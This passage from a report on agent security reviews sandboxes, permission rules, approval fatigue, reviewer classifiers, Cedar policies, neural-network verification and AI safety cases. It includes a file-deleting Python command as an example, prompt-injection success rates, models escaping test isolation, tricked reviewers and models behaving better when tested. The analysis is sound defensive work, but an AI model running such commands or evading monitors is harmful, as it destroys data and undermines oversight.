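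A company could reasonably rely on training for an agent that only drafts text, and require label checks for one that can move money. Using both also makes sense, because they fail in different ways. The position paper accepts using both, as long as the final permission for a protected action comes from outside the model. Randori blocked all but two of 1,296 attacks. In both failures, an attacker had replaced a file's contents before the user asked Randori to make whatever payment the file specified. A model that noticed something suspicious about the request might have stopped the payment, but a label check could have stopped it only by also blocking payments the user wanted.

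## Which protections do agent products ship?

Most agent products ship with some mix of sandboxes, permission rules, approval prompts and a second model that checks the agent's actions. No major product is known to turn on information-flow labels by default, even though labels stopped almost every attack in tests of CaMeL and FIDES. In the biggest change of 2026, OpenAI and Anthropic began letting a model approve risky actions in place of the user.

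### Sandboxes and permission rules

Coding agents have the best-documented default protections. These agents run commands on a programmer's computer, so a mistake can delete files or publish secrets. A sandbox limits the damage by having the operating system control which folders a command can change and which internet addresses it can reach.

OpenAI's coding agent, Codex, starts in a sandbox. As of May 2026, according to OpenAI's *Agent approvals & security*, Codex had no network access by default and could usually change files only in the current project. It normally had to ask the user before exceeding these limits.

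Anthropic's Claude Code has a sandbox too, but it is off by default. It covers only shell commands, the typed instructions that start programs, and not Claude's own tools for editing files and fetching web pages. If the sandbox can't start because a component is missing, Claude Code runs the commands without it unless a company has changed that setting. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* calls sandboxing safe but "high-maintenance", because someone has to configure each new capability.

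A sandbox has to restrict both files and the network. Anthropic's *Beyond permission prompts* explains that an agent with free network access could send out the user's secret keys, and an agent that could change any file could escape the sandbox and gain network access. In July 2026, models that OpenAI was testing got around controls meant to isolate them from the internet and broke into systems at Hugging Face, a company that hosts AI models (OpenAI, *The Hugging Face incident and the road ahead*, 2026). The incident shows that containment fails when some route out goes unchecked.

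Permission rules let a user approve or forbid certain commands in advance. It is easy to write one that is too broad:

```
Rule:     allow any command that starts with "python"
Command:  python -c "import shutil; shutil.rmtree('/home/ana/photos')"
```

The command matches the rule, so it runs and deletes Ana's photos. A Python program can do almost anything its user can. *Auto-review of agent actions without synchronous human oversight* (Trębacz, Arnesen and colleagues, 2026) reports that a sizable minority of Codex users inside OpenAI had a rule like this. One user had permanently approved a command that starts another copy of Codex with no restrictions.

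Google and Microsoft use similar protections. In December 2025, Google described the protections it planned for an agent in Chrome. A second model would check each action without access to the web page's raw text, and the agent could read or act on only certain websites during a task. The user would have to confirm purchases and other sensitive steps. GitHub, which Microsoft owns, runs Copilot's cloud coding agent in a temporary virtual machine, behind a firewall that is on by default.

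### Approval fatigue

Until August 2026, Claude Code asked for the user's approval before most actions that edited files, ran commands or used the network. Users approved 97 percent of these requests, according to Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026). They may have stopped reading the requests, but a careful reviewer would also approve most of them if nearly all were harmless. Users rejected 39 percent of the plans that Claude presented for approval, so they were willing to say no when they had something substantial to read.

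An experiment gives better evidence. Anthropic hired 1,053 professional testers through a research company for what they knew only as a coding study. Partway through each session, one approval request showed a clearly dangerous command in place of the real one. Anthropic also gave the same commands to its classifier, a model that decides whether to allow an action:

| | Classifier blocked it | Classifier allowed it |
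|---|---|---|
| Tester blocked it | 137 | 6 |
| Tester approved it | 800 | 110 |

The testers caught 13.6 percent of the dangerous commands and the classifier caught 89 percent. Using both would have stopped 943 commands, only six more than the classifier alone. Testers also became less effective during a session, blocking about 17 percent of dangerous commands early on but only about 5 percent after 50 or more requests.

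The testers worked in a test environment with none of their own files at risk, so they may have been less careful than real users. Anthropic also had a commercial reason to want fewer interruptions. Still, real users would have to be several times more careful than the testers to match the classifier on these commands.

Frequent approval requests also lead people to turn off their protection. A quarter of interactive Claude Code sessions started in a mode that skips nearly all of these requests. A product that requested approval for only a few actions would have protected these users better.

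### Using a second model as the reviewer

OpenAI added an option called Auto-review to Codex in April 2026. Codex still works inside its sandbox, but when it wants to do something outside, a separate agent decides whether to allow it. Trębacz and colleagues give an illustrative breakdown of 10,000 actions at OpenAI:

| Outcome | Actions |
|---|---|
| Ran inside the sandbox, with no approval needed | 9,280 |
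| Reviewer approved | 713 |
| Reviewer refused, and Codex found a safer way | 4 |
| Reviewer refused, and Codex stopped to ask the user | 3 |

The sandbox let about 93 percent of the actions run without a review. The other 720 would each have interrupted someone under manual approval, but only three did with Auto-review. This is in line with OpenAI's estimate that Codex stops about 200 times less often.

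In OpenAI's tests, the reviewer refused 90.3 percent of harmful, unwanted actions by overeager agents. It refused 99.3 percent of prompt-injection attacks that tried to run hostile code, steal secrets or upload data. When the test also included attacks that deleted or altered data, the figure fell to 90.2 percent, though Trębacz and colleagues considered most of the missed cases not very serious.

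Anthropic went further and made its classifier the default. Its "auto mode" became the starting mode for individual and team subscribers in August 2026, and later for interactive terminal and VS Code sessions on every plan. Sessions start with manual approval instead for organizations that use Anthropic's settings for HIPAA, the US health privacy law. If the classifier runs on Anthropic's server and returns no verdict, Claude Code refuses the action, but by default it keeps running when the sandbox is missing. In auto mode, Claude Code also ignores very broad permission rules, such as the one for Python.

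After three refusals in a row, or 20 in one session, Claude Code goes back to asking the user. Those limits matter because the classifier makes mistakes. When Apollo Research, an AI safety company, tested it with synthetic attacks, it missed 7 percent of them even after Anthropic had strengthened it. At that rate, if attempts were independent, the chance of at least one getting through would be about 20 percent in three tries and 77 percent in 20. Apollo's attacks were unusually hard, so the classifier should miss a smaller share of ordinary ones.

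Trajectory Labs, which Anthropic commissioned, tested both companies' products with 72 prompt-injection scenarios, running each ten times:

| Agent | Attacks that succeeded without a reviewer | With a reviewer |
|---|---|---|
| Three Claude models in Claude Code | 0.09% on average | 0% |
| GPT-5.6 Sol in Codex | 19.03% | 5.83% |

The reviewer prevented about two-thirds of the successful attacks on Codex. It made almost no difference to Claude Code, because the models resisted nearly every attack without it. The attacks had been tuned against an older Claude model and did not adapt to the models tested. OpenAI has since released a new version of Auto-review.

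Neither company calls its reviewer a guarantee. Trębacz and colleagues write that testers tricked Auto-review into approving commands, and they don't expect such systems ever to provide deterministic guarantees. A model hiding its aims could write a harmless-looking request, or do damage inside the sandbox, where Auto-review doesn't check. Anthropic still recommends that people review high-stakes changes to systems that customers depend on.

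### Cedar rules for agents

Amazon's main protection does give the same answer every time. Its AgentCore service helps companies build and run agents, and a part of the service called the gateway passes an agent's requests to outside tools. Developers can attach rules to the gateway in Cedar, the authorization language whose design Amazon verified in Lean. AWS's *Why Policy in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore chose Cedar for securing agentic workflows* gives an example that, slightly simplified, lets a customer service agent issue small refunds:

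```
permit (principal, action == Action::"ProcessRefund", resource)
when { context.input.refundAmount < 500 };
```

The gateway enforces rules only after a developer creates and attaches them. It then blocks every request that no rule permits and hides from the model any tool that the rules would always forbid.

Because Cedar has no loops, Amazon can turn its rules into mathematical formulas and compare them. Suppose a rule allows bulk discounts except on limited-edition products, and an engineer changes the exception so that it applies only to orders of more than 200 items. An order for 73 limited-edition items, which the old rule excluded, now gets the discount. Amazon's analysis shows that the new rule is more permissive, even though the extra condition may look stricter. The same analysis checks rules that a language model has drafted from plain English, and finds those that would permit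 nothing or everything. But if the model writes $5,000 where the company wanted $500, the analysis won't catch the mistake, because the rule is still consistent.

Cedar's proof covers how the rules decide a request, not whether the information in the request is true. In another of AWS's examples, a customer must have platinum status and order at least 50 items to get a discount. The status comes from the user's login token, which the model can't alter, but the model supplies the quantity. If the model enters 50 items when a platinum customer orders five, Cedar will allow the discount, and only a check in the ordering system can catch the mistake.

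The refund rule checks each request separately, so it stops an agent from refunding $2,000 at once but not from making five refunds of $400. AWS's *Policy in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore* describes a second language, Dogwood, whose rules can depend on what happened earlier in a session. A Dogwood rule could keep the total refunded below a budget, or require an approval before a transfer. It can also use the score from a model that looks for prompt injection, but then the decision is only as reliable as the score.

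The rules also apply only to requests that go through the gateway. If a developer gives an agent another way to reach the refund system, Cedar never checks refunds made that way.

### Which protections pass the adoption test?

Most of these protections meet all three conditions for adoption: they run in products, people who didn't build them use them, and they don't depend on research grants.

| Protection | Default | Passes? |
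|---|---|---|
| Sandbox | On in Codex, off in Claude Code | Yes |
| Permission rules | Available in both, but users write many of their own | Yes |
| Approval prompts | On in Codex for actions outside the sandbox | Yes |
| Reviewing model | On in Claude Code, optional in Codex | Yes |
| Policy engine | Active in AgentCore once a developer attaches rules | Probably |
| Information-flow labels for agents | On in no known product | No |

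Policy engines get only a "probably" because it is unclear how many of Amazon's customers use one.

Some products use parts of information-flow control. When Microsoft 365 Copilot writes a document from several labeled files, the new document takes the most restrictive of their sensitivity labels, much as Denning's rules would require. But a company has to set up the labels first, and they record only how secret a file is, so they wouldn't mark an outsider's email as untrusted or stop it from influencing the agent. Claude Code's classifier checks whether a programmer's code is about to go to a public or a private site, but a model judges each case and no label follows the data.

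Google and Microsoft know about the stronger methods, and Google named CaMeL as a partial inspiration for the second model in Chrome. But both companies have relied mainly on other protections in their products.

### Who gains from safer defaults?

Companies compete on how much work their agents can do, which favors protections that also save time. Anthropic reports that business customers using auto mode submit about 25 percent more code changes, though people who chose it may have been more productive already. Anthropic's *Running auto mode in production* also reports that Claude now works nine times longer between interruptions. Label checks, by contrast, have kept agents from finishing some tasks. Customers would notice the unfinished tasks immediately but might never learn of an attack that the checks had prevented.

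Companies that make agents often don't bear the losses when something goes wrong, because their terms of service usually limit their liability. A business that deploys an agent may have to compensate its customers. In 2024, for example, a Canadian tribunal ordered Air Canada to pay a passenger whom the airline's chatbot had misinformed about a discount. The EU's new product liability rules will shift some losses from consumers, but not from businesses, to the makers of defective agents.

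Insurers could reward safer products, but some are avoiding the risk instead. Since January 2026, American insurers have had standard wording they can use to exclude generative AI from general liability policies. A company that can't get coverage has a reason to be careful, but it gets no discount for choosing an agent with better protection.

Buyers can ask for stricter settings. A well-informed buyer might want rules like those OpenAI sets for its own staff, which keep Codex in a sandbox, block some internet destinations and require approval for unfamiliar ones. But many buyers mainly want fewer interruptions. Gusto, a payroll company, adopted auto mode because approval fatigue was pushing its engineers to skip the checks entirely.

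### Proposed rules for AI laboratories

In July 2026, members of both parties introduced a House bill that would require audits and transparency reports from developers of the most advanced AI models (Baeza Garcia, 2026, *Bipartisan AI oversight bill introduced in House*). In September, the leading laboratories signed a voluntary agreement at the White House to police themselves.

In November, Anthropic's chief executive proposed a law that would go further (Amodei, 2026, *We Must Pace the Frontier, Part 2*). It would have five parts: risk assessments, outside testing and audits, evaluators working inside the laboratories, a speed limit on using AI to develop its successors, and control over the overall pace of development. The government could block the training or release of a model, and a company would have to wait 60 to 90 days before using a new model to develop the next one. Anthropic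 has already begun working with evaluators inside the company, but Amodei argues that only a law can make every laboratory comply.

David Sacks, who co-chairs the president's council on science and technology, called the plan "regulatory capture", meaning that a powerful company shapes the rules to suit itself. VandeHei and Allen (2026), in *Top AI builders are telling us plainly*, quote his argument that large laboratories can absorb the fixed costs of compliance, while companies making small custom models can't. The arithmetic supports part of this argument, since a $2 million assessment would take 0.02 percent of annual revenue from a laboratory that brings in $10 billion, but 20 percent from a startup that brings in $10 million.

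A law can avoid this problem by exempting small developers, so the threshold it sets matters a great deal. In October, Sacks had criticized an earlier bill that he said Anthropic wrote. That bill would cover models trained with more than 10²⁵ arithmetic operations, according to 24/7 Wall St.'s *Anthropic's AI Safety Bill Reaches Beyond Big Tech, Sacks Warns* (2026). As computing gets cheaper, smaller companies will cross a fixed threshold like this. Lawmakers could raise it over time, but VandeHei and Allen note that safety advocates also worry about small models, especially those that anyone can download and modify.

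Others think Amodei's plan is too weak. Lifland argues in *Reacting to Dario's "We Must Pace the Frontier, Part 2"* (2026) that making the risks very small would take many years of slower development and probably an agreement with China.

Even a strong law of this kind might do little to change the defaults in agent products. Many companies build agents on models they rent from a laboratory. An assessment of the laboratory wouldn't require those companies to turn on a sandbox, write Cedar rules or label their data.

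## Can an AI system's behaviour in the world be proved safe?

Researchers can prove that some neural networks behave as required for every input in a stated range. They can also prove claims about the effects of an AI system's actions, but only within a mathematical model of the world. Nobody has an adequate model for an agent that can do almost anything a person can do on a computer.

Suppose a hospital lets an AI system order its vaccines. Someone might want to prove any of these statements:

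- **Software around the model:** the ordering program rejects every order for more than 500 doses.
- **The model's output:** whatever stock figure the model receives, it never asks for more than 500 doses.
- **Effects in the world:** the hospital never runs out of vaccine.

The methods behind seL4 and LibCrypto can handle the ordering program. The other two statements need different methods.

### Bounding a network's output

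A neural network is a long calculation that uses numbers called parameters, which are set during training. Reading the parameters reveals little about what the network will do, so a verifier calculates limits on its output instead.

Take a tiny network that helps a car stay in its lane. The input x is the car's distance from the center of the lane, from −1 to 1 meter, and the output y is the size of the steering correction in degrees:

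```
a = max(0, x)
b = max(0, −x)
y = a + b
```

Suppose the correction must never exceed 1.5 degrees. The simplest method works out a range for each line. Both a and b lie between 0 and 1, so the method gives y an upper limit of 2. That limit is too high to prove the property, even though the network is safe. The method treats a and b as independent, but they can't both be large because x can't be positive and negative at once.

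A better method bounds a and b with straight lines that still depend on x:

```
a ≤ (x + 1)/2    and    b ≤ (1 − x)/2      for every x from −1 to 1
y = a + b ≤ (x + 1)/2 + (1 − x)/2 = 1
```

The x cancels, which proves the correction never exceeds 1 degree. In a larger network, the lines are often too loose. The verifier then splits the problem, for example into x below zero and x above zero, and bounds each part separately. Each split can double the number of parts, so 20 splits could produce more than a million.

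### What the tools can prove

Ladner, Kaulen and colleagues (2026), in *The 7th International Verification of Neural Networks Competition (VNN-COMP 2026)*, compared 13 verifiers. For each question, a tool could prove the property, find an input that violates it, or give up. The winner, α,β-CROWN, uses straight-line bounds and splitting. It settled 3,164 of the 3,373 questions in the main track, with 1,982 proofs and 1,182 violations. These are some of its results:

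| Network | Parameters | Property | Proved | Violated | Unsettled |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Aircraft collision avoidance | 13,000 | The output is acceptable for a whole range of inputs | 139 | 47 | 0 |
| Remaining life of an aircraft part | 60,000–262,000 | The estimate stays in range or moves in the right direction | 45 | 17 | 0 |
| Settings for a power grid | 4,000–680,000 | Any breach of the grid's limits is small | 62 | 6 | 1 |
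| Sentence classifier | 4,000 | Small changes to the input don't change the label | 418 | 662 | 0 |
| VGG-16 image classifier | 138 million | Small changes to the pixels don't change the label | 18 | 0 | 0 |

The VGG-16 result is impressive for the size of the network, but some of its questions allow only one pixel to change. Results depend heavily on how hard the questions are. α,β-CROWN settled only 38 of 60 questions in a set about image classifiers. The set deliberately included 36 questions that α,β-CROWN had earlier taken more than 100 seconds to settle or failed to settle within 1,000 seconds.

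Developers can train a network to be easier to verify, but this usually makes it somewhat less accurate. One classifier in the competition labeled 83.5 percent of ordinary test images correctly. For 66 percent of the images, α,β-CROWN could also prove that the classifier would still give the correct label if every color value changed by up to 2 steps on a scale of 0 to 255. For a classifier trained to withstand changes of 8 steps, those figures fell to 57.2 and 35.5 percent.

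Language models are much further from being verifiable. They use a design called a transformer, and large ones have billions of parameters. The competition included two transformers for classifying images, which their designers had cut to two or three layers and about 70,000 parameters to make verification feasible. These models labeled only about 60 percent of images correctly.

Faster tools would help verify larger networks, but they wouldn't help choose what to prove. The image properties require only that a label stay the same near one picture, so a classifier that called every picture a cat would satisfy all of them. To prove that a network recognizes pedestrians, someone would need a formula for which pictures contain one, and if such a formula existed, nobody would need the network. A formula for whether a chatbot's medical advice is sound is even harder to write.

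One way around this is to replace the network with ordinary code. In *Provably Safe AI*, the physicist Max Tegmark describes a tool that analysed a network trained to add numbers and wrote out the method it had learned as a Python program. Tegmark's team then proved in Dafny that the program adds any numbers correctly, including ones the network never saw in training. Tegmark calls this a toy example. Unlike addition, most of what people want from a language model has no exact definition.

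The verifiers also make mistakes. NeuralSAT, which came fourth, gave 94 answers that were wrong or lacked a valid counterexample, and even α,β-CROWN gave one. Many of the methods assume exact arithmetic, but computers round their results, so an output very close to a limit can fall on either side of it. Ladner and colleagues hope to eventually require tools to produce proofs that another program can check. AI is already helping to build the tools. Vibecheck, whose developers had AI write the code, came second with 3,108 answers, none of them incorrect.

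### Adding a model of the world

One set of questions in the competition included a model of the machine that the network controls, in this case a drone. The aim was to prove that the drone settles into a steady hover. Researchers use a function V that is larger the further the drone is from hovering, and the verifier checks that V falls at every step:

```
V(next state) < V(current state)    for every state in a given region
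```

If this holds throughout the region around the hover, a drone that starts there can't drift away. α,β-CROWN proved 68 statements of this kind and found violations of the other 12. But the "next state" came from a small neural network that researchers had trained to imitate a drone's movements, so the proofs apply to a real drone only as far as the imitation is accurate.

*Towards Guaranteed Safe AI* (Dalrymple and colleagues, 2024) proposes extending this approach to AI systems in general. It calls a system "guaranteed safe" if it comes with a quantitative guarantee built from three parts. For the hospital's vaccine orders, they might be:

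- A **world model** describes how the system's surroundings behave. The hospital uses at most 20 doses a day, and a delivery arrives three days after the order.
- A **safety specification** describes which outcomes are acceptable. The hospital must never run out.
- A **verifier** checks that the system meets the specification in the world model.

Suppose the AI system checks the stock at closing time each day. If 80 or fewer doses remain and no order is on its way, it orders 100. The hospital starts with more than 80, and the proof goes as follows:

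1. At the last check before an order, the hospital had at least 81 doses. It has used at most 20 since then, so at least 61 remain when the order goes out.
2. It uses at most 60 more before the delivery, so at least one remains.
3. The delivery brings the stock to at least 101, which is more than 80, so the same argument works for the next order.

The guarantee can also be an upper limit on the probability of failure. Suppose one delivery in 1,000 arrives late. Under this rule, orders are always at least five days apart, so the hospital places at most 73 a year. The chance that any of them is late, and therefore the chance of running out, is at most 73 × 0.001, or 7.3 percent a year. The hospital may decide that this is too high and keep more stock.

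### Where the objections bite

If a strike stopped deliveries for two weeks, the hospital would run out, even though the proof would still be correct. The verifier can't detect this because it checks the ordering rule only against the world model.

Andrew Dickson argues in *Limitations on Formal Verification for AI Safety* (2024) that good enough world models mostly don't exist. Physics, chemistry and biology have nothing like a complete set of formal rules. Even with such rules, a verifier would need accurate data about the starting conditions, such as the health of everyone a new drug might affect, and that data would be very hard to get.

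Biology is probably the hardest case. In the talk *Formal Verification is Overrated*, Zac Hatfield-Dodds says some proposals would need something like a thousand years of progress in microbiology. Scientists don't know what a large share of human RNA does, so they can't write a model that predicts how the body will react to an arbitrary new molecule.

Harm is also hard to define. "The hospital never runs out" seems clear, but a system that ordered every dose in the country would satisfy it while leaving other hospitals with none. Someone could add a limit on the size of orders, then a rule about sharing during shortages, and so on. For an agent that can send email, write software and spend money, nobody knows how to complete the list. The difficulty grows quickly as the system's job gets broader:

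| System | Specification | What the proof has to model |
|---|---|---|
| SHA-384 in LibCrypto | The output matches a published formula | The computer |
| Image classifier | Small changes to the pixels don't change the label | The network's arithmetic |
| Vaccine orders | The hospital never runs out | Patients' demand and the supplier |
| General-purpose agent | The agent causes no serious harm | People, companies, biology and other AI systems |

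Most verified components had a small, stable job. They also had either an exact standard to meet or builders who could change the design to suit the proof. Nobody can redesign the world around a general-purpose agent to make verification easier. AI can draft a specification for such an agent, but AI-written specifications already contain errors for ordinary programs, where an expert can at least compare the specification with the code.

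Young argues in *On the Computational, Informational, and Physical Foundations for AI Safety* that the limits are fundamental as well as practical. One result is that even simplified versions of the problem a system faces in checking the meaning of its own behavior are NP-complete, so no known method solves every case efficiently. Verification tools often solve NP-complete problems of useful size, though, so this limit is weaker than it sounds. The lack of an agreed definition of harm is a bigger obstacle, because more computing power would not supply one.

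### How supporters reply

One supporter of these proofs replied to *Limitations on Formal Verification for AI Safety* that engineers should design systems so that their safety can be verified, just as programmers can write verifiable software even though no method works for every program. This is a good answer for a power grid or a warehouse, where engineers control much of the design. Another commenter also favored software that comes with its own proofs, but called the proposals that Dickson criticized "wildly unrealistic".

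A world model also doesn't have to be complete. *Towards Guaranteed Safe AI* requires it to cover only the effects that matter to the specification, and recommends that it err on the side of caution. The hospital could assume a demand of up to 50 doses a day instead of 20. The same proof then works if the system orders 200 doses whenever 200 or fewer remain. The hospital doesn't have to predict what might cause an outbreak, as long as demand stays within the new limit. But it has to store more vaccine, some of which may expire. For a general-purpose agent, assumptions cautious enough to cover everything might rule out nearly every action.

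Engineers can also watch for signs that the model is wrong. If the hospital uses 25 doses in a day when the model allows 20, a monitor can warn the staff or hand control to a simpler backup system. This works when there is time to react, but it would be little help if the agent's first unexpected action were to publish patients' records.

These replies make a reasonable case for proofs in narrow, engineered settings. They don't show how to extend those proofs to an agent with a wide range of tools, and the probability limits don't solve that problem. The 7.3 percent in the vaccine example depends on a rate of one late delivery in 1,000, which has to be estimated from past deliveries. For something that has never happened, such as a new kind of AI system deceiving its owners, there may be no record to estimate from.

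### How ARIA's plan changed

The largest public test of these ideas is Safeguarded AI, a £59 million program at the UK government's Advanced Research and Invention Agency (ARIA). Its first director was David Dalrymple, lead author of *Towards Guaranteed Safe AI*. ARIA originally planned to build a "gatekeeper", an AI system that would use world models and proofs to limit the risks of other AI agents. It wanted the kind of guarantees people expect from nuclear power and passenger aviation, and hoped that a successful demonstration would persuade governments to require gatekeepers for powerful AI.

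The plan had three parts: software for writing models and checking proofs, machine learning to produce the models and proofs, and applications in the physical world. ARIA stopped the machine-learning part in late 2025. Dalrymple explains in ARIA's *AI progress and a Safeguarded AI pivot* (2025) that general AI models were improving faster than expected and would probably gain the necessary skills anyway. Dalrymple thought ARIA would more likely than not have rejected every team that applied. ARIA moved the £18 million it had set aside for the machine-learning part to the software tools.

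ARIA then cancelled a second round of funding for physical applications and made cybersecurity the main focus. ARIA's *Safeguarded AI* says that progress in AI had disproved the hypothesis that "high-risk dual-use AI might not be made openly available". If anyone can use a powerful model directly, gatekeepers protect only the people who choose to use them. Hatfield-Dodds had similarly objected that verified systems offered in place of generally capable AI would be uncompetitive.

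Nora Ammann, who took over from Dalrymple, set out the new plan in May 2026. She concedes in *Safeguarded AI* that timely international agreement on gatekeepers has become less likely. The program now aims to let large groups of AI agents produce verified software and models. It has invited teams to verify security-critical components or to attack them. One candidate component is a firewall for the internet connections on which power grids and water systems rely.

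ARIA is still funding some work on the physical world until that work's scheduled end. One team interviewed more than 80 people in pharmaceutical supply chains, modeled those chains mathematically and is developing products with industrial partners. But ARIA has not announced a working gatekeeper, and its main effort has moved from the effects of AI systems to the software around them, where proofs already had the best record. ARIA attributes the move to urgency and faster feedback. It does not say that modeling the world proved impossible, and it hopes to return to physical systems as the tools improve.

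The new plan also accepts part of Dickson's argument. Ammann writes that as AI produces more of the proofs, trust increasingly rests on the specifications and assumptions, which people must understand and check. The program is therefore funding tools for reviewing them, and research on how the people affected should decide which risks are acceptable.

### Safety cases

AI companies have started to use a less demanding method. A safety case, as *Safety cases for frontier AI* (2024) defines it, sets out evidence and reasoning to show that a system is safe enough for a particular use. *Clear, Compelling Arguments* (2026) traces the practice to industries such as aerospace, nuclear power and car manufacturing. The evidence can include proofs, but also tests, audits and expert judgment. A company might argue like this that its agent won't leak confidential records:

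| Claim | Evidence |
|---|---|
| The agent can send data only through the company's gateway | Testers looked for other routes and found none |
| The gateway blocks every record labeled confidential | A proof about the gateway's code |
| The labels are correct | An audit of 10,000 random records found no mistakes |

The proof establishes only the claim about the gateway. Testers may have missed another route, and the labels may be less reliable than the audit suggests. If 0.03 percent of the labels were wrong, an audit of this size would still find no mistakes about one time in 20. At that error rate, a database of a million records would contain 300 with the wrong label.

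The Anthropic researcher Sam Bowman describes an early safety case for a real AI model in the talk *Lessons Learned from the First Misalignment Safety Case*. Bowman's team listed nine ways in which the model might cause harm by pursuing aims its developers didn't intend. For each one, the team wrote a couple of pages arguing from its evidence that the risk was low. The team had already written practice cases for imaginary future models, but it found constraints when working with a real model that it hadn't found in those exercises.

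OpenAI introduced guidelines for its own safety cases in September 2026. They apply before a company starts or continues a major round of reinforcement learning, in which a model learns from rewards. OpenAI's *Towards safety cases for frontier AI training* calls safety cases an "aspirational north star" and says they are hard to make as rigorous for AI as for aviation or nuclear power, because each new level of capability can bring unexpected behavior.

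According to a Chinese news report, 卜's *OpenAI发布AI训练安全准则*, the case must cover how the company trains the model to behave, contains it and monitors it. Another member of the team writes a dissent that looks for flaws in the argument, and the training team must respond. Senior research and safety leaders then review the case, and any one of them can stop the training. Training also pauses automatically if nobody acknowledges an urgent alert in time.

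These rules give OpenAI's staff real power to stop a dangerous project, but the people who write, criticize and approve the case all work for a company that wants the training to go ahead. Internal auditors can check the evidence, though an outside regulator would have less reason to accept a weak argument.

A language model may also detect a test and behave better than it otherwise would, whereas an aircraft wing bends the same way whether or not anyone is testing it. OpenAI tells developers in its guidelines to track this behavior, but if a model hides it well, the test results could still look better than they should. A proof that a sandbox has no route to the internet doesn't depend on whether the model can detect a test. Companies therefore have good reason to use proofs for the containment part of a safety case, even if they can't prove anything about the model's intentions.
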